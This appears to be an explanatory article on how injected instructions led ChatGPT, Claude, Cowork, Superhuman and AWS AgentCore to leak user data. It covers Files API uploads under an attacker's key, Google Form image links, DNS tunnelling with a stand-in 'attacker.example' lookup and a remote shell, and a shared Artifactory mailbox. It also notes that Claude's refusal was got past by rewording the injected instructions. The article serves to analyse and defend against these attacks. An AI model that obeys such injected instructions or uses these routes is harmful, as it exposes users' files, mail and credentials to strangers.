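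*The Read-Only Lie*, a post on the blog אִם יִרְצֶה הַשֵּׁם that the blogger drafted with AI help, estimates that the attack sent out about 143 bits in roughly 30 requests. Each page had 27 links, one for each letter and one for a hyphen, so each request carried about 4.75 bits. Claude had worked out Paul's home town from the name of a high-school hackathon, so the attack took a fact he had never told it directly. The stolen data came from Claude's memory of earlier conversations, not from an uploaded file.

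Anthropic removed web_fetch's ability to follow links inside pages it has fetched. It did not pay Paul a reward, saying it had already found the problem internally. As a result of the change, Claude can no longer follow a link from a table of contents to a chapter unless the user supplies the address or a search returns it. *The Read-Only Lie* suggests a compromise in which Claude could follow links only on sites the user has named in the conversation.

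OpenAI's rule would probably have stopped Paul's version without a ban on links. His site generated pages as Claude requested them, and each address contained all the letters sent so far. Ten characters from a 27-character alphabet produce about 200 trillion possible addresses, and a crawler could have recorded only a tiny fraction of them. Radware's numbered addresses would be harder for the rule to block, because a few hundred pages are enough and an attacker could get that many indexed.

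### Caching and a ban on repeat visits

After reading OpenAI's paper, Rehberger proposed two further defences on Embrace The Red. The assistant could cache each page, keeping a copy for a few minutes and using it if the model asks for the page again. Or it could refuse to visit the same full address twice in one session. In either case, the attacker's server would receive only the first request for each character, so if the model spelled "hello", the second "l" would be missing.

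If the attacker has only one address per character, this would prevent them from receiving most secrets in full. For example, only about 0.4% of nine-digit numbers have no repeated digit, so almost all would arrive incomplete. ChatGPT may already have part of this defence. Before November 2025, Tenable noticed that ChatGPT answered questions about a page it had already opened without visiting the page again. Rehberger had not checked whether OpenAI used either measure when he proposed them.

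Radware had published a way around both of them about a month earlier. If addresses are numbered by character position, an "l" in third place and an "l" in fourth place have different addresses, so the model never needs to open the same one twice. A nine-digit number would then require 90 public pages instead of ten. Alternatively, an attacker could write the number in binary and assign one page to each of its 30 binary digits. The model would open a page for each one and skip it for each zero, and the order of the requests would not matter.

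Caching and a ban on repeat visits force an attacker to prepare more pages, but they do not limit how much data the model can send. A cap on requests would. In 2023 Rehberger suggested that ChatGPT display at most a handful of images in each answer, which would have slowed attempts to spell out data through image requests. A cap on page visits would hinder users more, because research tasks can require an assistant to open dozens of pages.

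Rehberger was also concerned that OpenAI's developers might not apply the rule everywhere, which he calls a typical problem in large engineering organisations. ChatGPT has had such gaps. The first url_safe check did not cover the phone app, and ZombieAgent worked through connected email a month after OpenAI tightened the check. Yang, Na and Choi's February 2026 result with ChatGPT 5.2 may reflect another gap, since the address that reached their server contained a birth date and was unlikely to be in a public index.

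OpenAI began offering Lockdown Mode, its optional limit on outgoing requests, to personal accounts in June 2026. Willison approved of it because it relies on fixed rules that a prompt cannot override, however persuasive it is. He also inferred from its existence that ChatGPT's default settings do not robustly protect against a determined attacker. Dane Stuckey, OpenAI's chief information security officer, said the mode was meant for people whose identity, work or the data they handle puts them at higher risk, and that for them the protection was worth losing some features.

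## Claude: files sent to an attacker's account through an allowed domain

Rules about web addresses limit what the assistant's browsing tool and the user's browser can request, but they do not affect a program in the sandbox that opens its own network connection. OpenAI did not allow such connections in ChatGPT. In 2025 Anthropic gave Claude's hosted interpreter network access, and researchers soon found that code in the sandbox could send out whole files directly.

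The access is meant for installing software packages, which Claude downloads from public collections called package registries. Under the "package managers only" setting, the sandbox can reach only the domains on a short allowlist, which Anthropic publishes on its help page. The list includes GitHub, where programmers store and share code, and the download sites for JavaScript, Python and Rust packages and for Ubuntu, a version of Linux. It also includes two Anthropic domains unrelated to installing packages, statsig.anthropic.com and api.anthropic.com.

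Developers' programs send requests for Claude to api.anthropic.com, each with an API key that identifies the account. The Files API, part of this interface, stores uploaded files so that the account whose key came with the upload can use them in later requests.

### Rehberger's attack of October 2025

Rehberger read the allowlist while the feature was still new and stopped at its first entry, api.anthropic.com. He wondered whether an attacker who had taken control of someone's Claude session could use this domain to reach the attacker's own Anthropic account. His first idea was to send stolen text as chat messages. Then he found that the Files API would accept entire files. His post on Embrace The Red describes the attack in this order:

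1. The user asks Claude to summarise a document. The attacker wrote it, and it contains hidden instructions together with an API key for the attacker's account.
2. Claude follows the instructions. It looks up the user's most recent conversation, using a feature that lets it search past chats, and writes the text to a file in the sandbox.
3. Claude runs a few lines of Python that upload this file through the Files API under the attacker's key.
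4. The sandbox lets the request out, because it is addressed to api.anthropic.com.
5. The file appears in the attacker's account, and the attacker opens it in a chat of their own.

The attacker supplies their own API key for the upload, whereas companies usually worry about attackers stealing a customer's key. The upload doesn't use the user's Anthropic account, and the attacker doesn't need to learn the user's password.

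Rehberger put the limit at 30 MB per file, citing Anthropic's documentation, and noted that the instructions could trigger several uploads. One upload could hold 3,000 spreadsheets, each large enough that spelling it out through fixed web addresses would take thousands of page visits. A later report on the same route gives a limit of 500 MB per file. Anthropic also limits files in the Claude app to 30 MB, which may explain the difference.

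In the demonstration, the attack stole a past conversation rather than a file the user uploaded. An uploaded file should be easier to steal this way because it is already in the sandbox, so Claude can skip the second step.

The attack worked on Rehberger's first attempt. Claude then refused for some time, until he reworded the instructions. He gives no success rate. Anthropic closed his report as out of scope within an hour, but by 30 October had told him that closing it was a mistake.

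He also objected to the setting's name, because a user who reads "package managers only" could reasonably conclude that the sandbox can only install software. He suspected that other domains on the list would allow similar thefts. To prevent this one, he suggested letting the sandbox communicate only with the logged-in user's account.

### PromptArmor's test on Claude Cowork

In January 2026 Anthropic released a preview of Cowork, its office agent, in which Claude can read and change the files in a folder the user connects. At the time, Cowork ran code in a virtual machine on the user's computer, so it was not strictly a hosted interpreter. But its network rules resembled the hosted interpreter's, blocking almost every domain but allowing api.anthropic.com.

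Two days after the release, PromptArmor showed that Rehberger's route also worked there. Its *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* describes a user who connects a folder of confidential property files, including appraisals and loan estimates. The user also uploads a skill file for real-estate work that they found online.

Skills are normally plain-text files, but this one was a Word document made to look as if someone had edited a skill in Word and saved it in the wrong format. The Word format let PromptArmor hide the injection in white one-point type on a white background, with almost no space between lines. A person reading the document would not have noticed it.

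When the user asked Cowork to analyse the folder using the skill, Claude read the hidden text, which contained instructions to find the largest file available and upload it to the Files API with the attacker's key. Claude uploaded a loan estimate that contained financial figures and parts of Social Security numbers. PromptArmor then opened a chat from the attacker's account and asked Claude questions about the document.

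Cowork did not ask the user to approve any of the steps. The user could see the upload command only by expanding a block labelled "Running command".

PromptArmor ran this test on Claude Haiku, one of Anthropic's smaller models. It also describes a second scenario with Claude Opus 4.5, which it considers more resistant to injection. A user developing an AI tool uploaded a malicious integration guide, and Opus 4.5 sent customer records to the attacker's account. This shows that a user could not rely on the stronger model to stop the theft. PromptArmor doesn't give the number of attempts for either model, so the attack's success rate is unknown.

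According to TechRadar's *It's not just OpenAI models escaping and running riot*, later versions of Cowork run in the cloud by default, although users can still choose to run it on their own computers.

### Oasis Security's search advertisement

The attacks by Rehberger and PromptArmor both required the user to open a file from a stranger. Elad Luz, research lead at Oasis Security, wanted an attack that would work in an ordinary claude.ai chat with no documents or connectors. In *Three Vulnerabilities, One Click*, Luz (2026) combined the Files API upload with two other flaws, which brought the instructions to the user.

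One flaw was in the links that pre-fill a message on claude.ai. The text box did not display certain HTML tags, the codes that mark up a web page, but claude.ai still sent them to Claude. An attacker could write instructions inside a tag, and the user would see only a harmless request, such as one for a news summary, and press Enter. The hidden instructions appeared in the conversation afterwards, when Claude might already have begun to act on them.

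The other flaw was that a particular claude.com link forwarded visitors to any address added to the end of it. Google requires an advertisement to display the same domain as its link, so an attacker could use the forwarding link to buy a search advertisement that displayed claude.com but took people looking for Claude to the prepared message. Google also lets advertisers choose their audience by location, profession or a list of email addresses, so the attacker could target particular people. Luz shows previews of such advertisements but does not report trying them on the public.

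He says he chose the Files API to get the data out because two other methods had problems. Claude tended to refuse to open a suspicious web address with data at the end, and its page-fetching tool was unavailable until the second message of a chat, whereas the hidden instructions arrived in the first. He then considered, much as Rehberger had at first, having Claude's code send the stolen text to Anthropic as an ordinary prompt under the attacker's key. But the attacker could not have read the text, because Anthropic does not let account holders look up the prompts sent with their keys.

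An account holder, even one with a free account, can list its files at any time. They cannot download an uploaded file directly, but they can start a conversation that refers to it and ask Claude to read out the contents.

In Luz's demonstration, Claude searched the user's earlier chats for a message about health, saved it as a file in the sandbox and uploaded it to the attacker's account. Rehberger also took text from past chats. A file the user had uploaded could be sent out the same way, since the upload command works on any file in the sandbox. Luz writes that his final wording worked consistently, again without giving counts.

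Oasis published the report on 18 March 2026, after informing Anthropic. By then Anthropic had fixed the issue of hidden text in prepared messages. It was still working on the other issues, including the upload route, which Rehberger had reported almost five months earlier.

### Why the destination check let the upload through

Anthropic described the failure and the fix in a May 2026 article about Cowork and its other products. Cowork's outgoing traffic passed through a proxy that checked each request's destination against the allowlist. According to Anthropic, the proxy had to allow api.anthropic.com because Cowork cannot work without the company's API. In the first version, the whole agent ran inside the virtual machine, so even Cowork's requests for Claude's next step had to go through the proxy.

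Suppose Cowork sends two requests while it works through the folder of property files. It uses one to get the next step from Claude, with the user's session credentials. The other uploads the loan estimate with the attacker's API key. Both go to api.anthropic.com over an encrypted connection. A proxy can see the domain name without decrypting the traffic, but it can't see the key or the file. A proxy that checks only the domain will therefore allow both requests.

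Checking which function the code called would not have been enough either, because Cowork could use the same Files API to upload the same loan estimate to the user's own account without any outsider receiving it. The upload is a theft only because the key belongs to somebody else, so telling a theft from a legitimate request required checking the account. Anthropic could have blocked every upload from the virtual machine, but that would also have blocked legitimate ones, and an attacker might have found another function that stores data.

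Anthropic's servers read the key to put the file in the right account, but they cannot detect the theft, because the key is valid and every legitimate upload also goes to the account that its key belongs to. Anthropic's engineers say that the server cannot distinguish Cowork's requests from those of any other program that uses the interface. The server has no information showing that the request began in somebody else's Cowork session. The user's internet address would not reliably supply this information, because a developer may run Cowork and several unrelated programs on one computer, each with a different key.

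A company can give the server part of this information. In a guide for security teams, Pluto Security, another security company, describes an Enterprise setting under which a company's network adds its organisation number to all traffic bound for Anthropic. Anthropic then refuses requests from accounts outside that organisation. The setting is meant to stop employees from switching to personal Claude accounts, but Pluto says it also covers API keys, so it should reject an attacker's key sent from Cowork on an office computer. It would not protect the hosted interpreter on claude.ai, because that traffic starts on Anthropic's machines and never crosses the company's network.

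### The session-token proxy

Anthropic's fix added a proxy inside the virtual machine that intercepts every request to Anthropic's API. Each Cowork session receives its own token, a temporary credential with limited powers, and the proxy passes only requests that carry it. The user's main credentials stay outside the virtual machine. If the proxy had been in place during PromptArmor's test, Claude would still have read the hidden text and might still have tried the upload, but the proxy would have rejected the request because it used the attacker's key.

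Anthropic's fix is close to the one Rehberger proposed in October 2025. He wanted the sandbox to accept only the logged-in user's account, and Anthropic's version accepts only one session of that account. Anthropic can also cancel the token without cancelling the user's own login.

The proxy has to decrypt the request to read the token. The program connects to the proxy as if it were api.anthropic.com, and the proxy decrypts the request, checks the token and forwards the request to the real server over a second encrypted connection. A program would normally reject a connection to a stand-in server, but this virtual machine has an added certificate that makes its programs trust the proxy.

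According to Anthropic, the proxy also blocks headers (settings sent with a request) that would enable Anthropic's servers to fetch something themselves. Otherwise, code in the virtual machine could presumably have sent a request with the correct token and had an Anthropic server visit an attacker's address, since the server is not subject to the virtual machine's allowlist.

In March 2026, Pluto Security examined Cowork by reading its logs and program files and inspecting the virtual machine's disk. Pluto Security's *Inside Claude Cowork* confirms that the virtual machine generates a new certificate each time it starts and keeps the private key only in memory. Anyone who obtains the key can use it only until the next start, which limits the damage.

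Pluto says the proxy runs on the user's computer, outside the virtual machine, but Anthropic says it runs inside. Pluto's own evidence gives Anthropic's version some support, because the proxy's certificate has the name of coworkd, a service that Pluto found running inside the virtual machine. Pluto may have conflated this proxy with the one that enforces the allowlist, which does run outside.

Where the proxy runs matters if an attacker's code takes full control of the virtual machine, because the code might then be able to switch off a proxy running inside it. Anthropic acknowledges that only protections outside the virtual machine's operating system would survive this. Code that Claude runs starts with an ordinary user's permissions and would have to exploit a flaw to gain full control. TechRadar reports that the research company Accomplish AI used a Linux flaw to break out of Cowork's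 virtual machine in 2026. The researchers were trying to reach files elsewhere on the Mac, and TechRadar does not mention any test of the proxy. An attacker who only gets Claude to run an upload command, as in PromptArmor's test, does not have full control of the virtual machine.

### An allowlist entry permits everything the domain can do

The Cowork leak led Anthropic's engineers to describe an allowlist entry as a "capability grant", because it permits every function that the domain offers. They had previously thought of the allowlist as a list of destinations that Claude could safely contact. By allowing api.anthropic.com, they had also allowed uploads to any Anthropic account.

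Superhuman, an email program with an AI assistant, had a similar problem with a Google domain. Its Content-Security-Policy allowed the user's browser to load images from docs.google.com, which hosts Google Forms as well as Google's documents. Anyone can create a form and collect the answers. A form accepts answers written into a web address, so requesting that address is enough to submit them.

PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes an attack in which the instructions arrive in an email that the user doesn't have to open. When the user asks for a summary of recent mail, the assistant ends its answer with an image whose address points to the attacker's Google Form and contains the text of other emails. The browser sends that text when it requests the image, and Google stores it as a submission to the form. One response from the assistant leaked several complete emails,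 and another leaked parts of more than 40.

This attack works like the 2023 image leak, but the attacker doesn't need a server because Google receives and stores the data. PromptArmor reported the flaw on a Friday night in December 2025, and Superhuman disabled the affected features the following Monday. The same trick with a form later worked on OpenAI's coding agent, Codex. PromptArmor reported that flaw in April 2026, and OpenAI fixed it.

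PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* shows how the poisoned software guide led Antigravity, Google's coding tool, to steal credentials and code through its built-in browser agent. The browser's default allowlist included webhook.site, which gives any visitor a web address and displays every request sent to it. Developers use the service for testing, but an attacker can use it to collect stolen data. Its place on an allowlist is even harder to justify than that of docs.google.com. A vendor might allow docs.google.com for its documents and overlook the forms, but the main function of webhook.site is to show incoming data to whoever created the address.

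Anthropic could keep its own domain on its list of allowed domains and make it safer, because it issues the tokens that Cowork's requests carry. Superhuman's requests to Google Forms had no such token to check. A vendor in that position has to permit a narrower set of addresses, restrict what its assistant may display, or remove the domain.

Other entries on the default list for Claude's interpreter could be misused in the same way. PromptArmor's *What domains should I add to my allowlist?* (2026) points out that anyone with a free account can publish a package on npm, the main registry for JavaScript. An injection could therefore tell an agent to put the user's data in a package and publish it where the attacker can read it. On GitHub, the agent could upload the data to a public repository. PromptArmor advises companies to check whether each domain accepts uploads under a key that an attacker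 could supply, as the Files API did and as npm and GitHub do. PromptArmor presents npm and GitHub as risks to consider and does not demonstrate a theft from Claude through either.

Pluto Security reports in a revised version of its post that Cowork's session-token proxy decrypts only traffic to api.anthropic.com. Connections to GitHub, npm and the Python registry stay encrypted, and Cowork checks only the hostname, so it cannot detect whether a program is downloading a package or publishing one, or whose account it is using. Pluto originally wrote that Anthropic could inspect all of the agent's encrypted traffic. It changed this after finding that only Anthropic's domain had a certificate issued by the proxy, while the other sites presented their own.

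Anthropic could decrypt those connections too, but this could break programs that carry their own list of trusted certificates and ignore the one that the virtual machine adds. Pluto notes that such programs can reach the Python registry today because the proxy leaves the registry's certificate alone. Even with the traffic decrypted, the proxy would need rules for each service about which requests publish data, and for GitHub it would have to check which accounts the user is allowed to write to. A simpler rule would allow downloads from the package registries and block all uploads to them, since installing software requires only downloads. Programmers who use Cowork to send code to their own GitHub repositories would need an exception.

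### Whether claude.ai received the same repair

Anthropic's May 2026 article describes the session-token proxy only for Cowork's virtual machine. It treats the hosted interpreter on claude.ai as a separate design and mentions no check on API keys there. But Rehberger and Luz had both demonstrated the upload on claude.ai, and Rehberger did so before Cowork existed.

Anthropic's current help page for the hosted interpreter still lists api.anthropic.com among the approved domains. The page describes several protections, such as a classifier for injected instructions and a time limit on tasks, but none of them concerns the account that a request uses. Anthropic still warns there that hidden instructions could make Claude read sensitive data and leak it through a network request from the sandbox, and advises users to watch Claude and stop it if it does something unexpected.

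*Claudy Day* (Luz, 2026), Oasis's shorter account of its findings, gives slightly more recent evidence than the technical report. It states that Anthropic has fixed the prompt injection and is still addressing the other issues. Oasis last updated the post on 27 May 2026 but may have done so without rechecking this statement, so the date is weak evidence that the route was still open then.

The help page doesn't show whether the upload still works on claude.ai either. Cowork's repair left api.anthropic.com reachable and only restricted who could use it, and Anthropic could have done the same for claude.ai without changing its list of domains. This might even be easier on claude.ai, because all traffic from the hosted sandbox starts on machines that Anthropic controls. The company could therefore check the key outside the sandbox, where the attacker's code cannot interfere. But neither Anthropic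 nor Oasis has published a statement that the upload no longer works on claude.ai.

Until one of them does, a cautious user should assume that code in the claude.ai sandbox can still upload files to an attacker's account when network access is on. Turning off network access blocks this route, because the upload has to start from inside the sandbox. It is also unclear whether the fix covers the cloud version of Cowork, because Anthropic's account of it describes a virtual machine on the user's computer.

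## Leaks from sandboxes described as having no internet access

With network access switched off, code in a sandbox cannot connect to Anthropic's Files API or any other outside server. Vendors usually mean this when they say a sandbox has no internet access, as OpenAI does of ChatGPT's. Amazon Web Services (AWS) originally advertised one mode of its interpreter as "complete isolation with no external access", according to the security company BeyondTrust (2026). Both sandboxes blocked ordinary outside connections, but code in either could still look up domain names. Code in ChatGPT's sandbox could also reach a service inside OpenAI's network that other customers' code used. In 2026 researchers published demonstrations in which either route alone was enough to steal data.

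### Why a lookup delivers data

Computers find each other by numerical addresses, so a program that has only a name, such as shop.example, must first obtain the number. DNS, the domain name system, supplies it in several steps:

1. The program hands the name to its operating system, which sends it to a resolver, a server that looks up names for many machines. In a hosted sandbox, the resolver usually belongs to the vendor or its cloud provider.
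2. The resolver checks whether it has a recent copy of the answer. If it does, it returns the copy and the lookup ends there.
3. If it has no copy, the resolver contacts a root server, which returns the addresses of the servers responsible for the ending, here .example.
4. One of those servers returns the address of the name server for shop.example. The domain's owner chooses this name server and can run it on a machine of their own.
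5. The resolver sends the name to that name server, which returns the numerical address.
6. The resolver passes the address back to the program, which can now try to connect.

A rule that blocks outside connections takes effect only after the sixth step. By then, the domain's name server has already received a message that originated in the sandbox.

An attacker can use that message to carry data, because the owner of a domain controls every name under it and a program can look up a name that doesn't exist. Suppose the attacker again owns attacker.example, and code in the sandbox looks up `lee-85.attacker.example`. Nobody has looked up this name before, so the resolver has no stored answer and must send the name to the attacker's name server. The attacker finds "lee-85" in the server's log, even if the server replies that the name doesn't exist. To protect users' privacy, some resolvers withhold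 the full name from the root servers and the servers for the ending, but they still have to send it to the domain's own name server, since only that server can answer.

The attacker can also send data into the sandbox. The attacker chooses which IP addresses the name server returns, and code in the sandbox can decode them as text instead of connecting to them. With enough lookups, the code and the attacker can exchange messages without connecting to each other directly, because the resolver relays every query and answer. This technique is called DNS tunnelling, and it is much older than hosted interpreters.

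### The "personal doctor" GPT

ChatGPT's sandbox allowed such lookups until February 2026, according to *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026), which the security company Check Point's research arm published on 30 March. The researchers could not reach an outside server from the container in the ordinary way, which matches OpenAI's documentation. Lookups worked because they were part of the environment's normal operation.

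OpenAI had put safeguards on the more obvious routes, including its rules on web addresses. When a custom GPT uses a feature called Actions to send data to an outside service, ChatGPT shows the user what will be sent and where, then waits for approval. The lookups triggered no warning or approval request. Check Point Research says this happened because the model assumed the sandbox could not send data out, and so did not treat the lookups as a transfer, but it doesn't describe a test of this explanation. The approval dialog belongs to Actions, so code in the sandbox might not have triggered it whatever the model assumed.

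The hostile text reached ChatGPT in one of two ways. In the first, the user copied a prompt from a website or forum and pasted it into a new chat. From then on, every message the user sent could leak. What leaked depended on the prompt's wording and could include the user's own words, text from an uploaded file, or the model's conclusions. Check Point Research suggests that an attacker could present the prompt as a productivity aid or as a trick for unlocking paid features on a free account. Someone hoping to unlock features already expects the prompt to look odd, so a long, unreadable passage would not put them off.

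The other way was a custom GPT with the instructions built in. The user only had to open the GPT and start talking to it, so an attacker did not need to persuade anyone to copy a prompt. OpenAI does not let builders read other people's conversations with their GPTs, but a builder who used this weakness could have obtained the contents.

To demonstrate this, the researchers built a GPT that acted as a personal doctor. The user uploaded a PDF of laboratory test results that included the patient's name, described some symptoms and asked for help understanding the results. While the GPT gave a medical assessment, the researchers' server received that assessment and the patient's identity. When asked, ChatGPT told the user that the data had not gone anywhere. The attacker did not need the PDF itself, because the name and the assessment were the most sensitive parts of the conversation and both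 were short.

The researchers could also send commands into the container and receive the results through the same lookups. This gave them a remote shell, meaning they could type commands on another computer to control the Linux environment that ChatGPT had created for that user's code. A remote shell makes the attacker much less dependent on the model. In most of the attacks on ChatGPT and Claude, the model has to carry out every step of the theft and may refuse at any of them. With a remote shell, the attacker only has to get the model to start one program, which then runs the attacker's commands without the model reading them and returns the output without displaying it in the chat. Check Point Research does not claim to have reached other customers' containers this way.

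Check Point Research shows the attacks in videos but gives no success rate and does not name the model it tested. OpenAI confirmed that the route existed, told the researchers it had already found the underlying problem internally, and finished deploying a fix on 20 February 2026. Check Point Research does not describe the fix or give the date of its own report, so outsiders cannot tell how long lookups had been open. It reports no theft from an actual user.

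### A CSV file in Amazon's Sandbox mode

AWS sells a hosted interpreter, AgentCore Code Interpreter, to companies that want their chatbots and agents to run code. It is part of Amazon Bedrock, AWS's service for building AI products. The developer chooses one of three network modes. Public mode gives the code open internet access. VPC mode places it in a private network where the developer sets the rules. Sandbox mode is supposed to let the code reach only S3, AWS's file storage service.

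BeyondTrust writes that access to S3 was a key requirement for customers. Code that uses S3 has to look up the service's IP address, and AWS said that it had enabled DNS for this purpose. However, the resolver also accepted names unrelated to S3.

BeyondTrust's researchers discovered this on 1 September 2025 by having the interpreter contact a server that records incoming lookups. The attempt appeared to fail inside the sandbox, but the lookup had reached the server. Testing a sandbox only from the inside would therefore give a misleading result. The blogger who could not open outgoing connections from ChatGPT's sandbox showed that connections were blocked, but not whether lookups were too.

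AWS asked for a fuller demonstration with two-way communication, and BeyondTrust built one that starts with a CSV file. If a chatbot includes the file's contents in the model's prompt, an injection in the file can make the model write a Python program that repeatedly looks up names under the attacker's domain. The answers contain pieces of a command. The program assembles the command, runs it, and sends the output back in further lookups. Each malicious file has its own session number, so an attacker can tell hijacked sessions apart.

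The evidence is stronger for the network part of this attack than for the injection. AWS reproduced the two-way channel in October 2025, but BeyondTrust doesn't say which model read the CSV file or how often the model followed the instructions in it. The attack also works only if the chatbot lets a user's material influence the code, as data-analysis chatbots generally do. BeyondTrust points out that an attacker might not need an injection. The interpreter comes with more than 270 third-party packages, and a malicious version of one of them could open the same channel as soon as a program loaded it.

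Once the channel was open, the researchers used it to read files in cloud storage. AWS lets a developer assign the interpreter a role, a set of permissions for other AWS services, and commands sent through DNS ran with that role's permissions. The researchers used these commands to list the storage areas in their own account and print three files of invented data. One held customers' names, email addresses, telephone numbers and the last four digits of their Social Security numbers. The other two held payment-service keys and quarterly revenue figures. The contents of all three came back in DNS lookups.

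Nobody had uploaded those three files to a chat. The attacks on ChatGPT and Claude steal the user's own file or conversation, but in BeyondTrust's attack the user can be the attacker and the company that runs the chatbot can be the victim. Suppose a shop builds a customer-service chatbot on AgentCore and lets people attach order lists. A stranger could attach a malicious CSV file and, if the interpreter's role has access to other customers' records, might be able to read them.

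The interpreter's role may well have access to more than the chatbot needs. BeyondTrust found that the default role in an AWS starter kit could read every S3 storage area in the account and had full access to the account's DynamoDB databases and stored passwords and keys. A developer can also give the interpreter a role intended for another part of AgentCore, with permissions the interpreter doesn't need. If the role could read only the one storage area the chatbot needs, an attacker with the same open DNS channel could steal much less.

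BeyondTrust does not report whether code in Sandbox mode could write to an S3 bucket in someone else's AWS account. S3 uses the same addresses for all AWS customers, just as Anthropic's API does for all of its own customers, so a rule that allowed S3 traffic without checking the account would have had the same weakness as the allowlist entry in Cowork. Under such a rule, an attacker could have copied whole files directly, without using DNS.

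AWS closed the DNS route on 15 April 2026, a month after BeyondTrust published its findings and several months after AWS decided to change its documentation rather than the product. Eight days before the fix, Palo Alto Networks' research team Unit 42 also published a demonstration of DNS tunnelling from the same sandbox. *Cracks in the Bedrock* (Hadad, 2026) covers exposed credentials as well. BeyondTrust's attack sent data out through a network function that AWS had deliberately switched on, so it did not require a flaw in the virtual machine. BeyondTrust praises AWS for the strength of the virtual machine's isolation, which is better than some competitors offer.

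### How much a lookup can carry

DNS limits each part of a name, the text between two dots, to 63 characters. BeyondTrust's program put at most 60 characters of encoded data in each lookup. The encoding uses 64 different characters, so each one carries 6 bits, and 60 of them carry 45 bytes. Sending one megabyte therefore takes about 22,000 lookups.

| Data sent | Size in bytes | Lookups needed |
|---|---|---|
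| The two-line order file from the 2023 example | 22 | 1 |
| BeyondTrust's three demonstration files | 601 | 15 |
| A summary of about 300 words | 2,000 | 45 |
| A small spreadsheet | 10,000 | 223 |
| A one-megabyte file | 1,000,000 | 22,223 |
| A 30 MB file, Rehberger's limit for the Files API | 30,000,000 | 666,667 |

An attacker could send the same data in fewer lookups. A complete name can have up to 253 characters, enough for three blocks of 60, so a megabyte would take about 7,400 lookups. Compressing the file first would reduce that number further. But some lookups may get lost, and one missing piece can make the rest of a compressed file unreadable, so the program would have to number the pieces and resend some of them.

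Each lookup carries much more data than a visit to one of the fixed web addresses that got around OpenAI's rules on links. Sending the small spreadsheet would take about 15,500 page visits with 36 addresses, compared with 223 lookups. Lookups are also more reliable, because a program copies the bytes exactly and ChatGPT only has to write that program once. When ChatGPT spells out a secret by opening pages, it has to choose each page correctly.

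DNS is slower than an upload, though. Neither Check Point Research nor BeyondTrust gives a transfer speed. If a program managed 20 lookups a second, the spreadsheet would take about 11 seconds, the megabyte 19 minutes and the 30 MB file more than nine hours, by which time the session might well have ended. Commands travel into the sandbox more slowly than data travels out, because a numerical address has room for only a few characters. In BeyondTrust's demonstration, a six-letter command took four DNS answers. This hardly hinders an attacker, since commands are short.

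A large theft should be easy to notice if someone is monitoring the lookups. A few hundred strange lookups might go unnoticed among the thousands that an office network produces each day, but a program that adds up sales figures in a hosted interpreter has little reason to look up outside names, and 22,000 different names under one domain would be conspicuous in any log. An alarm based on volume would still miss a password, which fits into a single lookup. In ChatGPT's case, the monitoring is up to OpenAI, because the lookups start on its side. Neither Check Point Research nor BeyondTrust reports that a vendor's monitoring detected the tests.

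These limits make summaries much more attractive to an attacker than full documents. A summary takes 45 lookups however long the original document is, and the assistant can write it as part of the attack. Check Point Research argues that an attacker may prefer the model's conclusions regardless of these limits, such as the main terms of a contract or the findings of a financial analysis. A summary also leaves the attacker less to read. However, it may contain the model's mistakes, and the attacker cannot check it against the original.

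Credentials are even better suited to a slow channel, because a short secret can give access to a lot of data. Sending out the key to a payment service takes one or two DNS lookups. The temporary credentials for an AWS role are longer, perhaps a thousand characters, and would take a little over 20. Someone who obtained them could often use them from their own computer until they expired, and download files from S3 at full speed over an ordinary connection instead of DNS. BeyondTrust notes that another security company, Sonrai Security, had earlier extracted credentials from AgentCore's interpreter.

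### Data passed between ChatGPT accounts

Anthropic let Claude's code reach the public package registries so that it could install software. OpenAI kept ChatGPT's containers off the internet and gave them an internal copy of the packages through JFrog Artifactory. This is safer in one respect, because the code has no direct connection to a public registry where an attacker could receive data. But different customers' containers all used the same internal service.

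Check Point Research published a second report on ChatGPT, *The Shared Clipboard Inside the Sandbox* by Alexey Bukhteyev, on 8 September 2026. It showed that containers belonging to different ChatGPT accounts could exchange data through Artifactory. ilSoftware.it's *ChatGPT, un canale nascosto permetteva di sottrarre dati tra account* describes the method. Artifactory can attach properties, which are name-value pairs, to a stored item. Each ChatGPT container had credentials for fetching packages, and the researchers found that these credentials also let the container change some properties. From one account they wrote a test value to a property of a stored file, and from a second account they read it. Data too long for one property could be split across several, according to the researchers' account in TechRadar's *A worrying ChatGPT bug let strangers read Gmail messages*.

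The properties worked like a mailbox that both accounts could open. In outline, the attack went as follows:

1. The attacker, using their own ChatGPT account, leaves a task in a property.
2. The victim sends an ordinary message in a chat that already contains the attacker's instructions. ChatGPT answers the message and also fetches the task.
3. ChatGPT carries out the task with the permissions the victim has given it.
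4. The result goes into another property, and the victim sees only the answer to their own question.
5. The attacker's container reads the result.

In the demonstration, the task was to retrieve email data from the Gmail account the victim had connected to ChatGPT. The Gmail connector is separate from the sandbox, so the model presumably copied the email text into code that wrote it to the property. The attacker did not need a server, malware or the victim's password.

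The attack required the victim to bring the planted instructions into the chat. eSecurity Planet's *ChatGPT Flaw Let Attackers Secretly Hijack a Victim's AI Session* (2026) lists three ways this could happen. Two of them, a copied prompt and a custom GPT, are the same as in the "personal doctor" research. The third is a link to a shared ChatGPT conversation. A person who opens the link and sends a message continues a conversation that already contains the instructions. The victim also had to have connected Gmail or some other source worth reading.

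The attacker could have used a different task to request other data. Gulf News' *ChatGPT security flaw raises concerns over private data* reports that previous conversations and files in the chat or its working environment were potentially accessible, and ilSoftware.it adds Google Drive, Microsoft Teams and GitHub for users who had connected them. The published demonstration took email, not an uploaded file. An uploaded file should have been easier to send because it is already in the container that writes the property.

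Commands sent through the remote shell in the earlier research ran in the container, so they could read what was stored there but could not by themselves search the user's mail. The tasks left in Artifactory went to the model, which could use every tool the user had connected. Unlike a shell, though, the model could refuse a task. None of the press accounts gives a success rate for the Gmail theft.

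OpenAI's description of the sandbox remained literally accurate during this attack, because neither container connected to the internet. The stolen mail went from one container to Artifactory, then to another container, and reached the attacker as output in an ordinary ChatGPT session. Rules on outgoing connections could not have stopped this, because the only destination was a service that the containers were supposed to use. The thefts through Anthropic's Files API similarly used the vendor's own service to move data from one customer's account to another's. The test also showed that one account's container could read what another's had written, so anyone else who knew where to look could probably have read the stolen mail too, unless the attacker encrypted it.

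The only sign of the theft was a small label, "Talked to Gmail", next to ChatGPT's answer. According to Mynavi News' *ChatGPTを悪用して他人のGmailを秘密裏に閲覧、OpenAIが対策を実施* (2026), the label appeared after ChatGPT had read the mail, so it could not help the victim prevent the attack.

OpenAI closed the route by retiring the Artifactory instance. None of the accounts gives the date, but according to eSecurity Planet, the channel was already gone when Check Point completed its report, which puts the closure before 8 September 2026. It is unclear whether Check Point's warning prompted the closure. Mynavi News presents it as OpenAI's response to the warning, but OpenAI's own experiments had given it another reason to retire the service.

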